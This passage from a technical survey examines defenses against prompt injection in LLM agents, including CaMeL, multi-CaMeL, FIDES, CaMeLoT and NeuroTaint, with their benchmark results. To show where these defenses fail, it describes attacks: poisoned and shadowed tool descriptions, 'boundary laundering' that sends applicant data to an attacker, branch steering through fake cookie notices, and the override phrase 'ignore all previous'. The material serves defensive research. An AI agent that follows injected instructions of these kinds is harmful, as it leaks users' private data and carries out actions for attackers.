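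Tallam and Miller propose screening the request before the planner reads it. Their screen would check the reputation of any links, look for phrases such as "ignore all previous", and measure how statistically unusual the text is. They report that this takes less than five milliseconds in internal tests. But the screen is a filter, and Nasr and colleagues showed that adaptive attacks easily get past filters, so a system that relies on it no longer has a guarantee for the request.

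Their other proposal keeps the protection in ordinary software. Every value from an uploaded file would carry a tag recording its origin, and policies would keep tagged values out of irreversible actions, such as sending external email, unless an authorized person grants an exception. But people often upload a file because they want the agent to act on it. An employee who uploads a supplier's invoice and asks the agent to pay it would need an exception every time.

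A tag also needs a boundary between the user's words and everyone else's, which text pasted into a chat box lacks, unlike a file. The interface could offer a separate field for pasted text and give the planner only a variable name, as CaMeL does with tool results. But if a user then pasted an email and wrote "deal with this", the planner would have to work out what that means without reading the email.

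### Tool descriptions

A planner learns what a tool does from a written description of its purpose and arguments. In a benchmark, the researchers control these descriptions. Many working agents instead get their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting agents to tool servers. *MCPGuard* (2025) notes that these servers come from companies and official maintainers, but also from open-source communities and individual developers.

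*MCP-ITP* (2026) describes what happens when an agent connects to an honest server and an attacker's server at the same time. The software loads both servers' tool descriptions into the agent's system prompt, where the attacker's description can influence how the model uses the honest server's tools, even if the model never calls the attacker's tool. In the Bob example, the description of an unrelated weather tool might state that every outgoing email must also go to a certain records address. The planner could then add that address to its program before anyone opens the meeting notes. Keeping the planner away from tool results does not prevent this. CaMeL and FIDES both treat tool descriptions as trusted, so a policy that checks only whether the recipient is trusted would pass the address. A policy that checks who may read the document could still block the email.

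A tool description can do harm without containing an instruction. *MCP-DPT* (2026) lists descriptions that promote a tool, for example as the "most accurate" one, so that the model picks it over a safer alternative. A filter that looks for commands would miss these descriptions. According to *Labels Are Not Endpoints* (2026), researchers have also tested poisoned descriptions on real MCP servers and split one attack across several descriptions.

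Tool names are another weak point. *MCPGuard* describes tool shadowing, in which a malicious server registers a tool under the same name as a legitimate one. Because nothing separates the two servers' names or verifies where a tool came from, the agent's software may run the wrong tool. The planner's program would correctly call `send_email`, and its policy would approve the call, but the attacker's code would receive the document.

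CaMeL needs more detailed tool descriptions than an ordinary agent does. An ordinary agent can call a tool and look at the result, but CaMeL's planner has to write code to parse the result before the tool has run. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) ran CaMeL on two benchmarks whose tool descriptions did not specify the format of the results. They therefore added a full specification of the results to every description, as CaMeL's creators had done before them. They consider this a modest, one-time job for a given set of tools, but it would recur for an agent that keeps connecting to new servers. If the server's owner writes the specification, the planner also reads even more text from an outsider. Longer descriptions also increase the tokens and time each request takes.

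*Labels Are Not Endpoints* lists several defenses, including one that verifies actions before they take effect and one that inspects tool calls and their responses. Some of the checks rely on trained models, so adaptive attacks can beat them. An operator could instead review each tool description by hand, store the approved text and show the planner only that copy. This would also stop a "rug pull", in which a server changes a tool's description after the user has accepted it. However, the operator would have to review every legitimate update, and a reviewer who reads descriptions one at a time could miss an attack spread over several. The review also can't establish that a tool's code does what its description claims.

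### Messages from other agents

Developers increasingly split work among specialised agents. An orchestrator receives the user's request and calls other agents as if they were tools, and each of those agents treats the orchestrator as its user. Peters-Gill and colleagues asked whether such a system is safe if every agent runs CaMeL. They tested for control-flow integrity, which holds if all tool calls stay within a plan determined only by the user's instruction and other trusted information. Untrusted data may select a branch already in the plan, but it may not add one.

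Their example has an orchestrator, an agent that can query a database, and an agent that can send email and Slack messages. The user asks the system to "Send a summary of all job applicant info to Julie on Slack." An attacker has left a line in the database asking for the same information to go to an outside email address. The database agent's planner never reads that line, and neither does the orchestrator's. But the orchestrator's program ends by handing over the summary like this:

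```
notification_agent(f"Send this summary to Julie via Slack: {summary}")
```

The notification agent receives the whole string as its user's request. Its planner reads the attacker's line and writes a program that sends the Slack message and then emails the applicants' details to the attacker. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering, because untrusted text becomes trusted when it passes from one agent to another. They used GPT-5.2 for all the models and ran every agent without security policies. A policy on recipients might have stopped the email, but the planner would still have included the attacker's instruction in its program.

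They also prove that the problem affects any system of at least two agents, arranged as a tree, in which some agent has a tool that returns untrusted data. The proof assumes that users can ask an agent to call any of its tools and return the result, or to use one tool's result in a call to another. If the agent with the untrusted tool has an agent below it, some request makes it call the tool and put the result into its instruction to the lower agent. If it has only an agent above it, some request makes the upper agent ask it for the untrusted data and then call it again with an instruction that contains that data. In both cases, untrusted data ends up in an instruction that a planner reads. The proof does not show that such requests are common.

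Protecting each agent separately is still worthwhile. In an earlier attack called OMNI-Leak, text in a public database makes a database agent query a private database. The attack has to change that agent's own plan, and it failed in all five trials when every agent used CaMeL.

### Multi-CaMeL

The repair that Peters-Gill and colleagues propose, multi-CaMeL, gives each call between agents two separate parts. The orchestrator's last line would become:

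```
notification_agent(
    message="Send the summary to Julie via Slack.",
    variables={"summary": summary},
)
```

The notification agent's planner reads only the message. Its program can fetch the summary by name at run time, but the planner never sees the contents. The interpreter prevents any message from depending on a tool's output. It also preserves the capabilities of values passed as variables, so a policy in the receiving agent can check where a value came from. An orchestrator therefore can't mention a file name it has looked up, even one from a trusted directory. It has to pass the name as a variable, and the receiving planner must plan without knowing it.

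To test the design, they divided AgentDojo's tools among two to four agents per environment and added an orchestrator. They ran 949 attacks for each model and setting, and separately measured how many of the 97 user tasks each system completed when there was no attack. All numbers in the table are percentages.

| Model | Attacks that succeed, no CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL | Tasks completed, no CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
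|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1 | 0.5 | 0.0 | 78.4 | 38.1 | 24.7 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6 | 0.4 | 0.0 | 76.3 | 42.3 | 26.8 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1 | 0.0 | 0.0 | 27.8 | 13.4 | 7.2 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5 | 0.0 | 0.0 | 69.1 | 53.6 | 52.6 |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0 | 0.0 | 0.0 | 86.6 | 73.2 | 66.0 |

With CaMeL in each agent, about nine of 4,745 attacks succeeded, all through boundary laundering. Multi-CaMeL stopped all of them. The difference is weak evidence by itself, since zero successes in 949 runs is compatible with a true rate of up to 0.4 percent. The better argument for multi-CaMeL is that it removes the path the attacks took. The benchmark's attacks were fixed in advance, and an attacker who knew about the handover could write text designed to survive it. No attack succeeded against GPT-5.5 even without a defense, but that result has the same limitation, and Peters-Gill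 and colleagues warn against reading it as general resistance.

The drop in task completion depends heavily on the model. With multi-CaMeL, GPT-4.1 completed fewer than a third as many tasks as it did unprotected, while GPT-5.5 completed about three quarters as many. Claude Fable 5 often refused harmless tasks, perhaps because the benchmark looks like an attack. On the 45 tasks without refusals, it completed 91.1 percent unprotected and 84.4 percent under either version of CaMeL. On AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks, putting CaMeL in each agent lowered task completion by an average of 21.6 percentage points across the five models, and multi-CaMeL lowered it by a further 3.2 points.

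Multi-CaMeL covers only trees of agents, in which each agent takes instructions from one other agent and starts fresh with each call. Agents that share a memory or message each other freely would need the same separation on every channel between them. Multi-CaMeL also depends more on the interpreter than a single CaMeL agent does, where the planner is safe from tool results even without policies. The interpreter must correctly trace every message back to its sources, because one lost dependency would let untrusted text into a planner's instructions.

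### Tasks that depend on the data

Planning first works for the Bob request because the steps are the same whatever the notes contain. If the user instead asks the agent to do whatever Bob wants in his latest email, the planner can't know whether to send a file, book a room or pay a bill unless it reads the email, which is untrusted. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) describes this as a fundamental limitation of separating planning from reading. It arises whenever untrusted data specifies the sequence of actions.

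Less extreme tasks run into the same difficulty. Most of the failures that Peters-Gill and colleagues examined happened because the planner committed to a program too early. Sometimes a tool's result was needed to show that the task required another step, and the program had no branch for it. In other runs, an agent had no data for the requested machine or dates and returned data for something similar. The orchestrator's program was already written and used that data as if it were correct.

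Xiang and colleagues add that a fixed plan can break on ordinary faults, such as an outdated interface or a missing software package. By their account, only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 user tasks require a change of plan or policy, so the benchmark largely fails to measure this problem. *AgentDyn* (2026) introduces a benchmark with more such tasks. All the tested defenses built on GPT-4o completed far fewer tasks on it than GPT-4o did without a defense. Meta SecAlign had the best result, completing 53.4 percent of tasks, compared with about 80 percent on AgentDojo. Meta SecAlign is a trained model that doesn't plan in advance, so fixed plans can't explain its drop, but the drop does show that a good AgentDojo score is weak evidence of performance in changing environments.

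### A plan that hands control to a file

One way for a planner to handle a data-dependent task is to write a program that can do anything the data might call for. Garby and colleagues found this when they reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks with its policy checks switched off. In one task, the user asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planner couldn't see the instructions, so it wrote a loop with a case for each tool. A loop of this kind looks roughly like this:

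```
for step in steps_found_in_file:
    if step.action == "send_money":
        send_money(step.recipient, step.amount)
    elif step.action == "update_password":
        update_password(step.new_password)
    # and so on for the other tools
```

The planner never read the file, but it wrote a plan that treats the file's contents as instructions. An attacker who writes the file therefore decides which tools run, in what order and with what arguments.

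Garby and colleagues had sorted the 144 pairs of banking tasks and attacks into two groups. In 97 pairs, the attack needed a tool call that should never appear in a plan for the user's task, so separating the models should have been enough to stop it. For these pairs, CaMeL without policies resisted the attack in 98 of 99 completed runs with GPT-5.2 and 240 of 241 with MiMo-v2.5. Both failures came from the file task, where the planner's loop contained the calls the attacker needed.

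These runs didn't violate control-flow integrity as Peters-Gill and colleagues define it. The planner wrote every branch from trusted inputs, and the file's contents only determined which one ran. Control-flow integrity therefore protects a user only to the extent that the plan is narrow. A plan with a branch for every tool satisfies the definition but lets an attacker do anything the tools can do.

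With the policies on, CaMeL blocked every attack in the runs that finished. But when there was no attack, it completed only 18 of 48 attempts at the banking tasks, compared with 32 for GPT-5.2 and 34 for MiMo-v2.5 with the policies off. A system could also inspect each plan before running it and reject any loop that connects untrusted text to a wide choice of tools. That would stop this attack, but it would also block the task the user requested.

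### Steering among planned branches

A planner can also allow for what it can't know in advance by writing a branch for each situation it expects. Foerster and colleagues applied this to computer-use agents, which operate a mouse and keyboard and normally examine a new screenshot before each action. In their design, CaMeL-NOVA, the planner writes the complete program before any model has processed a screenshot. A quarantined vision model then describes the screen and locates buttons. At each branch point, another quarantined call checks whether the description meets a condition the planner wrote, such as whether a login page is open, and the interpreter takes the matching branch.

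These plans average 213 lines and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and about 4 branches for CaMeL's AgentDojo plans. Roughly half of the steps in the larger plans are fallbacks that don't run in a given session. The researchers report that the design retains up to 57 percent of a frontier model's performance on OSWorld, a benchmark of desktop tasks. For that figure, a task counts as solved if any of five attempts succeeds. On a single attempt, the agent solved 31 of the same 109 tasks, or 28 percent. The difference matters in real use because a user can't always undo what the agent did in a failed attempt, as a benchmark can by resetting the computer.

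An attacker can't add an action to such a plan, but can influence which branch runs by changing the vision model's input. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. For example, many plans include a routine for closing cookie notices. If an advertisement on a web page looks enough like a cookie notice, the vision model may classify it as one, and the program will then follow the planner's routine, click on the advertisement and open the attacker's site.

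Steering is easiest when one wrong answer is enough and the routine appears in nearly every plan. Steering toward an action such as a bank transfer is harder because the attacker would have to predict a particular plan and cause several wrong answers in the right order. Foerster and colleagues assume the attacker knows the task and can roughly predict the plan. They consider this realistic for someone who owns a website or advertises on one, because visitors to a site tend to want the same few things.

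In a text-based agent, a policy could catch some of these actions, for instance by checking an email's recipient. A computer-use agent's basic action is a click at screen coordinates, and the same click might log in, delete a file or open an advertisement. Coordinates give a policy little to check, so Foerster and colleagues left policies out and tested two other checks. One compares the screenshot with the web page's code, and the other uses a second vision model to confirm the first one's answer. They found attacks that got past each check, and the broader checks that caught more attacks also flagged more harmless tasks. CaMeL-NOVA alone uses 1.88 times as many tokens as the unprotected agent, and adding the second model raises this to 6.57 times. A better fix would translate clicks into meaningful actions that a policy can check, which they leave to later work.

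LLMbda's theorem for programs without endorsement rules out branch steering wherever the choice of branch would affect a trusted result, but control-flow integrity permits it. Peters-Gill and colleagues acknowledge that multi-CaMeL also permits it.

### Planning again along the way

The remaining option is to let the planner revise its plan. FIDES does this at every step while hiding untrusted results from the planner, except for yes-or-no answers and similar values that a policy may allow. Foerster and colleagues built a version of FIDES for computer use and found that it solved about as many tasks as CaMeL-NOVA. Their version used 29.6 times as many tokens as the unprotected agent because it sends the planner the full history before each action.

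Xiang and colleagues argue that general-purpose agents will have to update both the plan and the policies based on what they find. In debugging, for example, nobody can list in advance which files the agent will need to read or run. But every update gives untrusted data a way to influence the plan. Xiang and colleagues criticise Progent because it passes unrestricted tool results to a language model that can rewrite the policies, so an attacker can aim an injection at that model.

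Xiang and colleagues propose having a language model approve changes but restricting what it reads. The model would receive each proposed change in a fixed, structured form, without the surrounding web page or error log, and would decide only whether the change is acceptable. This gives an attacker much less room to manipulate the model than free text does, but the system's safety again depends on a model's judgment, although on a much narrower question. They describe telling harmless updates from malicious ones as the central research problem and don't claim to have solved it.

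Even a perfect judge could not tell whether some updates are safe. Xiang and colleagues give the example of a coding agent that finds instructions online to install a package that seems relevant to its task but is malicious. People follow such instructions too, often without checking them. The proposed update looks the same whether or not the package is safe, so they would leave such decisions to the user or to a rule made by the user's organisation.

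## Data labels and security policies

Even a flawless interpreter lets attacks through if the labels it reads or the policies it applies are wrong.

### Who assigns the labels

When Costa and colleagues labelled AgentDojo's data to test FIDES, they marked a field as untrusted everywhere if at least one of the benchmark's injection tasks placed text in it. One attack in the body of one email made the body of every email untrusted, while any field that the benchmark's creators never attacked stayed trusted. The researchers wanted a clear baseline, and this method does test whether FIDES works when its labels are right. But the operator of a working agent has no list of future attacks to base labels on, and a real attacker would look for fields that had been left trusted.

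A value can be accurate and still be chosen by an outsider. In the bank data, for example, transaction amounts counted as trusted. A bank records amounts accurately, but the sender of an incoming payment chooses the amount. If a planner changes the user's password after any unusually large transaction, a stranger could trigger the change by sending a large payment. The risk is much smaller than with a transaction's description, because an amount can't carry a written instruction.

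Email offers better evidence because, as Costa and colleagues point out, mail servers can authenticate a sender's address with DMARC, a standard for checking that a message came from the domain in its sender address. However, attackers can register a domain and set up DMARC for it correctly, so the operator also needs a list of trusted domains. Even a message from an authenticated address may be unsafe, since colleagues forward newsletters and quote customers, and someone may have taken over a colleague's account. It is safer to trust the address field but not the body.

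A trusted address field is useful even then. In one AgentDojo task, the user asks for a password reset link from their mailbox, and the planner fails to return the right one because it can't tell trusted senders from untrusted ones. Costa and colleagues suggest letting the planner see the labels so that it could return only links from trusted addresses.

Shared documents are harder to label. A drive's permission list shows who could have edited the meeting notes, but not who wrote the line with Bob's address. If one outsider has editing rights, the whole file is untrusted, even if colleagues wrote every word. Labelling each paragraph by its last editor would be more precise, but a trusted colleague can paste in text from anywhere. Nikolaou and colleagues describe a similar problem with calendar events, whose descriptions are trusted only if the user wrote them. Their checker runs before the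 agent has read any events, so it treats every such description as untrusted. This is a sensible default, since a wrong guess then blocks a task instead of letting an attack succeed.

Confidentiality labels can also list too few readers or too many. Costa and colleagues infer an email's readers from its sender and recipients, and they acknowledge that people may have shared it more widely. When the label omits those readers, the policy blocks harmless messages. Listing too many readers is more serious. A file's owner may let anyone with the link open it only to avoid adding colleagues one by one. The file's list of readers is then technically everyone, and a rule that compares recipients with readers would let the agent send the file to any address.

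In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) label sensitive records by owner, based on where the data came from. In their example, Jane's assistant has access to Mark's mental health diagnosis. Mark's ex-wife creates a shared page, fills in part of it and asks the assistant to add Jane's notes. The assistant treats this as ordinary teamwork and writes the diagnosis on the page. Shim and colleagues' system, FlowSeal, labels the diagnosis as Mark's and uses a check outside the model for every write to a shared page. This check runs even if the assistant doesn't recognise the disclosure. FlowSeal reduced leaks from this attack from 52.2 percent to 0.5 percent. Shim and colleagues exclude prompt injection, so their results don't measure how well labels for trust work.

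### Labels on what a model writes

FIDES gives a model's output the combined label of everything in its input. This is sound, meaning that the label covers every input that mattered, but strict, because it also covers all the inputs that didn't. In one Slack task, the planner looked up the channels even though the user had already named the channel, which lowered the trust in everything the planner did afterwards.

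Costa and colleagues describe two attempts to loosen the rule by estimating which inputs the model used. Siddiqui and colleagues identify the messages that influenced a response, have the model rewrite the response from those messages alone, and give it only their labels. RTBAS, a system by Zhong and colleagues, builds on this work. It estimates each input's influence either from the model's attention weights (internal numbers that determine how much the model draws on each part of its input) or by asking a model to judge it.

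If the model regenerates its response from only three trusted messages, a hostile fourth message can't contribute text to the new response. The fourth message may still have affected which three the system kept, but that gives an attacker far less influence. If a system instead keeps the original response and drops the label of any input that seems irrelevant, one wrong estimate marks an untrusted value as trusted. The system still applies the policy every time, but the protection now depends on a statistical estimate that an attacker can try to skew.

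*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and Tang, 2026) relies on estimates throughout. Its system, NeuroTaint, examines an agent's log after a run and looks for flows from untrusted sources, such as web searches and emails, to sensitive actions, such as sending mail or running code. It builds a graph of how data moved between tools. When the agent saves something to memory, NeuroTaint stores the labels with it, so a saved document still has its origin attached when the agent uses it three days later. A system that tracks labels only within one run would lose the origin.

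For each sensitive action, NeuroTaint runs up to five tests, starting with the cheapest.

1. It adds a unique random code to the source text when the agent reads it, and checks whether the code appears in the action's arguments.
2. It measures how much wording the source and the arguments share. It reports a flow if their longest common sequence is at least 15 percent as long as the shorter text.
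3. It converts both texts into vectors that represent their meaning, and reports a flow if the cosine similarity of the vectors is at least 0.60. Text retrieved from memory must reach 0.85.
4. It splits long sources into passages and compares each one separately, so that the rest of a long web page doesn't hide one hostile paragraph.
5. If nothing matches, it shows a language model the log alongside a copy in which neutral text, such as "No relevant information found", replaces the source. It then asks whether the agent would have taken the same action anyway. If not, NeuroTaint reports that the source influenced the decision.

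To test NeuroTaint, Cai and colleagues built TaintBench, which has 400 scenarios in 20 agent frameworks. In half of them, untrusted data is meant to reach or influence a sensitive action. NeuroTaint found 187 of these 200 flows and raised 16 false alarms on the other 200 scenarios. Most of the missed flows involved repeated paraphrasing, and most of the false alarms came from text that merely resembled the source or that the model could have written from general knowledge. NeuroTaint found 37 of the 40 flows in which the source mainly affected the choice of action.

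Cai and colleagues' version of FIDES found 108 flows and raised 106 false alarms, but this comparison reveals little about FIDES itself. FIDES blocks a call if untrusted data might have influenced it. TaintBench counts only calls that the data did influence, so it scores this deliberate caution as a false alarm. The 92 missed flows are harder to explain. In one scenario, a poisoned search result makes the agent send its research to an attacker's website. The loop that Costa and colleagues describe would label that call untrusted because the planner had read the search result. Their policy for consequential actions would then block it. Cai and colleagues' version instead looks for known paths between source tools and sensitive tools. It flagged nothing on four frameworks, which accounts for 40 of the misses.

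NeuroTaint's own score may also be too high. Cai and colleagues write that "safe-control policies" use a stricter similarity threshold of 0.95. If this refers to the harmless scenarios, they set the threshold knowing which scenarios were harmless, and false alarms would be more common in real use. They also didn't test attacks written to evade NeuroTaint. An attacker could reword a text until its similarity score falls below the threshold, or address instructions to the model that runs the last test, since that model's input includes the original log.

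NeuroTaint helps explain how an incident happened, but it can't prevent one because it examines the log after the agent has sent the email. An agent that used the same estimates to block actions in real time would miss some attacks, as any filter does. FlowSeal has a similar risk because it uses a model to compare protected records with a proposed output. The comparison runs outside the conversation, where an attacker has less influence over it, but between 0 and 3.3 percent of protected items still leaked across Shim and colleagues' tests.

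### One email policy, worked through

Even with perfect labels, someone has to turn them into a rule. A reasonable email policy, written as a Python function of the kind CaMeL uses, might look like this:

```
def send_email_policy(call, recipients, body, attachment):
    if not is_trusted(call):
        return Denied("Untrusted data chose this action.")
    allowed = readers(body) & readers(attachment)
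    if not set(recipients) <= allowed:
        return Denied("A recipient may not read the content.")
    return Allowed()
```

The planner must not have read untrusted data before deciding to send the email, and every recipient must have permission to read both the message and the attachment. The policy doesn't require the recipient's address to be trusted, because Bob's address comes from the untrusted meeting notes and would always fail.

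Suppose the document is a contract. The user, Ana and Bob may read the notes, and the user, Bob and Cem may read the contract. The agent found the contract's name in the notes, so the attachment gets the combined label of both files:

{user, Ana, Bob} ∩ {user, Bob, Cem} = {user, Bob}

The policy correctly allows the email if the notes contain Bob's real address, and correctly blocks it if someone has replaced that address with a stranger's.

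Now suppose Bob asked for the contract by phone and has no access to the notes:

{user, Ana} ∩ {user, Bob, Cem} = {user}

The policy blocks the email, even though Bob is allowed to open the contract himself and the user asked the agent to send it to him. The block keeps Bob from inferring that the notes mention this contract, but hardly any user would want to protect that fact. The labels record only which data a message depends on, not how much the message reveals.

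The same policy also misses an attack. Ana, who can edit the notes, saves a copy of the contract with her own bank account in it. She gives the user and Bob access to the copy and changes the file name in the notes. The planner chose to send the email based on the user's request alone, and Bob may read both files, so the policy allows the call. Bob receives the altered contract from the user's address and has little reason to doubt it. The attack works even though every label is correct, because the policy doesn't check who may have tampered with the attachment.

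Adding a line to the policy that requires the attachment to be trusted would stop Ana. It would also block every other version of the request, including the harmless one, because the file name always comes from the notes. Whoever writes the policy has to choose between these outcomes or make an exception for this case.

### Missing rules and broad rules

An organisation needs rules like this for every tool that can do damage. Tallam and Miller expect these rules to become hard to manage in companies with hundreds of tools, because different teams will write separate Python functions that duplicate or contradict one another. They recommend keeping the rules in one place, writing them in a language made for access rules, such as Rego, and reusing common ones such as "share only within domain". Their evidence comes from similar problems with configuration files for cloud systems, not from companies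 that run CaMeL. Correcting a shared rule updates every tool that uses it, but a mistake in the rule also affects all of those tools.

An obvious danger is that a security policy overlooks a tool. A company may write a careful rule for email but none for its calendar tool, which emails an invitation to every participant. An attacker can then put a secret in a meeting's title and add an outside address to the guest list. If the system allows calls that no rule covers, nobody notices the missing rule until an attack succeeds. If it refuses them, the missing rule shows up as a blocked task, and somebody will probably complain.

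A rule can also be so broad that it permits some attacks. When Costa and colleagues inspected the attacks that AgentDojo recorded as successful, they excluded some because the policy allowed the action. These included Slack messages that the agent sent after reading untrusted text, as long as the messages contained no links and revealed nothing to people without permission to read it. The count of zero successful attacks with policies switched on depends partly on these exclusions. Costa and colleagues reasonably distinguish permitted actions from failures to enforce the policy, but a permitted message can still harm a colleague, for example by persuading them to call a fraudulent phone number.

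### A gate on shell commands

Rules are easier to write for tools that do one thing. An email tool takes a recipient, a message and an attachment, and a policy can check each of them. Many coding agents have a shell, a single tool that can read files, install software, delete folders and contact any server. The command `curl` can download documentation or upload a private key, and `python build.py` can do anything the script contains. A rule that permits such a command therefore allows many different actions, including harmful ones, but forbidding it stops most programming work.

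In *INFUSE*, Nguyen, Guo and colleagues (2026) tested defenses in this setting. Their benchmark has 40 tasks, such as fixing a bug or deploying a program, and 56 attacks hidden in files, file names, terminal output and similar places. The agent works in an isolated container and issues one shell command per turn. A language model then reads the record of each run and judges whether the injected text changed what the agent did or decided to do.

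Nguyen and colleagues built a gate for this environment rather than porting all of CaMeL. The gate derives a policy from the user's request, freezes it so that later text can't change it, and checks the parts of each command that could have outside effects. If a command fails the check, the gate replaces it with a harmless placeholder. They also adapted Progent, a system that grants an agent only the permissions its task requires. They tested both defenses on the same 200 combinations of task and attack. The table gives the percentage of runs that the judge classified as compromised.

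| Model | No defense | CaMeL-style gate | Adapted Progent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-14B | 27.3 | 31.5 | 35.0 |
| Gemma-3-12B | 32.7 | 31.9 | 30.5 |
| GPT-4o-mini | 46.5 | 43.0 | 43.0 |
| Gemini-3.1-Flash-Lite | 55.5 | 55.2 | 63.5 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 6.5 | 9.2 | 27.1 |

Neither defense clearly reduced attacks on any model. The 95 percent confidence intervals overlap in nine of the ten comparisons. In the tenth, the attack rate for Claude Sonnet 4.6 rose with Progent. That increase may be misleading, because in the main benchmark a spending limit cut off some of this model's undefended runs and made it look safer than it was. Nguyen and colleagues limit their conclusion to their own adaptations of CaMeL and Progent for the shell.

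This caution is warranted because the gate does not separate the planner from untrusted data, and that separation provides much of CaMeL's protection. The model still reads every file and every line of terminal output before choosing its next command. All the protection therefore has to come from a rule about commands, the kind of rule that a shell weakens most.

The scoring may also understate the gates' protection. The judge counts a run as compromised if the agent adopts the attacker's goal, even if the agent fails to achieve it. If the model tries to upload a private key and the gate replaces the command, the key is safe, but the judge may still record a successful attack. The benchmark also checks for concrete results such as stolen files, but Nguyen and colleagues compare the gates using only the judge's verdicts. Those verdicts show that the gates didn't stop models from being persuaded,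 which no gate on commands could do, but leave it unclear how much damage the gates prevented.

Meta SecAlign, the model trained to resist injections, reduced the judged rate from 25.8 to 11.5 percent for the 8B version and from 29.6 to 7.8 percent for the 70B version. Training changes which actions the model attempts, so this measure captures its effect. But these attacks were fixed in advance, and Nasr and colleagues defeated the same defense almost every time with attacks that adapted to it.

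### Policies that a language model writes

No one can write a separate policy by hand for every request, so some systems have a language model write them. If a user asks to send Bob a contract, the model could permit one search of the notes, one file download and one email, and forbid everything else for that task. This policy would be much narrower than a permanent one that covers every possible use of the email tool.

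If the model writes the policy from the user's request before the agent reads anything else, and nothing can change the policy afterwards, an injected sentence can't loosen it. As Xiang and colleagues point out, Progent gives up part of this protection because it lets a model revise the policy after reading tool results. Costa and colleagues expect adaptable policies to make agents more useful, but they warn that relying on a model's decisions can weaken the guarantee.

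A frozen policy can still be wrong, even if software enforces it perfectly. The model might allow email to any address because the user didn't mention one, and Bob's forged address would then pass. It might also omit a tool that the task turns out to need.

Nikolaou and colleagues restrict what the model can write. Their optional extractor reads the user's request and proposes rules from a fixed list of forms, such as "b is allowed only after a" or "only these side effects may occur". Ordinary code rejects any rule that names an unknown tool or has the wrong form, then converts the rest into logical formulas. This guarantees that each rule is well formed and refers to real tools, but not that it matches what the user meant, because the model still interprets the request.

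### Checking the plan before it runs

CaMeL checks a policy at each tool call. CaMeLoT, which Nikolaou and colleagues built on CaMeL, also checks the whole plan before any tool runs. It converts the planner's program into a diagram with one state for each step and arrows to every possible next step. It labels each value by where the value will come from. A program called a model checker then searches every path through the diagram for one that breaks a rule.

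The rules are written in temporal logic, which describes what must hold over the course of a run. In one of Nikolaou and colleagues' examples, the planner's program reads messages from a channel, has the quarantined model find Bob's address in them, and sends a message to that address. The relevant rule is

**AG**(call_send_direct_message ⇒ recipient_trusted)

**AG** means "at every step of every path", so whenever the program sends a direct message, the recipient must be trusted. The address comes from the quarantined model, so CaMeLoT rejects the plan before the agent reads any messages. It then shows the planner the path that broke the rule and asks for a new plan. The new plan might get Bob's address from a trusted address book. If the address exists only in the messages, no plan can both satisfy the rule and complete the task.

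A plan that passes obeys the rule whatever the tools return, as long as the diagram represents the program correctly and the labels are right. This also holds for plans with loops, because the diagram allows any number of repetitions. However, the diagram can include paths that the program would never take, which can lead CaMeLoT to reject some safe plans. CaMeLoT also can't check policies that depend on facts known only during the run. Nikolaou and colleagues could reproduce 22 of CaMeL's 28 policies for AgentDojo, and the other six depend on information such as who can read a file at that moment. The email policy above compares recipients with readers, so CaMeL would still have to check it when the email is sent.

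CaMeLoT and CaMeL were both run on AgentDojo's 97 user tasks, without attacks, using Claude Haiku 4.5. In 22 tasks, the plans didn't do what the user wanted. Among the other 75, the systems made the same decision on 59, CaMeLoT alone allowed nine plans, and CaMeL alone allowed seven. CaMeL's checks still apply during the run, even when CaMeLoT has approved the plan. CaMeLoT's main practical benefit on these tasks is that it refuses a bad plan before the agent spends money on model calls or changes anything.

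CaMeLoT can also enforce rules that CaMeL's checks don't naturally express, because they concern the order of steps or something that must happen later. Nikolaou and colleagues demonstrate this with an agent that handles security alerts. One rule requires it to confirm which computer is affected before it disconnects that computer from the network:

**A**[¬call_isolate_host **U** confirm_host_called]

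On every path, the agent may isolate the computer only after calling the confirmation tool. Another rule states that if the agent opens a ticket, it must eventually resolve or escalate it. The evaluation used seven such rules, each with one plan that broke it. CaMeLoT caught all seven plans, and a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. The rules were chosen to go beyond what CaMeL can express, so the result shows what the logic can do but gives little evidence of how often it would help in practice.

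These rules can contain mistakes too, and a model checker will enforce a mistaken rule on every path. Nikolaou and colleagues describe one of their rules as requiring human approval before a strong action, but its formula checks only that the agent has called the tool that requests approval. In their example of a safe plan, the agent requests approval and isolates the computer on the next line, without using the answer. Unless the tool stops the program when a person says no, the plan can isolate the computer without approval and still satisfy the rule.

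## Untrusted values that policies let through

A policy that kept every untrusted value away from every consequential action would block much of what people want an agent to do. Costa and colleagues sorted AgentDojo's user tasks by whether the planner must see what the tools return to choose the right actions or reply. It must in about 44 percent of the banking tasks, 43 percent of the Slack tasks and 5 percent of the office workspace tasks. Someone who asks an agent to pay a bill or respond to a meeting request wants another person's text to affect what happens. Systems therefore let some untrusted values through, on the grounds that the value can do little harm or that the user meant to rely on it.

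### False answers from the quarantined model

Most of these values come from the quarantined model. It has no tools, but hostile text can still make it return a false answer, such as a forged address for Bob. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) gives the example of an agent that reads a calendar and then emails the user's boss. An injection in the calendar can change the body of that email to anything the attacker wants.

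The model can also misuse other data it receives. Dongol describes an agent whose quarantined model has access to both an incoming email and the user's private notes when it writes a reply. Normally, the model would base the reply on the email alone. After an injection, it quotes the notes, and the plan sends them out. Labels can stop this leak by marking any reply written with access to the notes as private. But a legitimate reply has the same inputs and therefore the same label, so the system blocks it too unless someone makes an exception.

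Developers can limit how many answers one hostile file can affect. *Design Patterns* describes a map-reduce design in which a separate model reads each file and returns only whether it contains an invoice. A hostile file can make the model that reads it answer wrongly, but it can't influence the models that read the other files.

### Ordering answers by capacity

FIDES bases its exceptions on how much information an answer can hold. When the planner sends a question to the quarantined model, it also specifies the answer's type, such as yes or no, one item from a list, or free text. Constrained decoding enforces the type by allowing only tokens that keep the answer within it. An attack may still cause the model to output yes when the correct answer is no, but it can't add other text to a yes-or-no answer.

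Costa and colleagues order the types by capacity:

bool ⊑ enum ⊑ string

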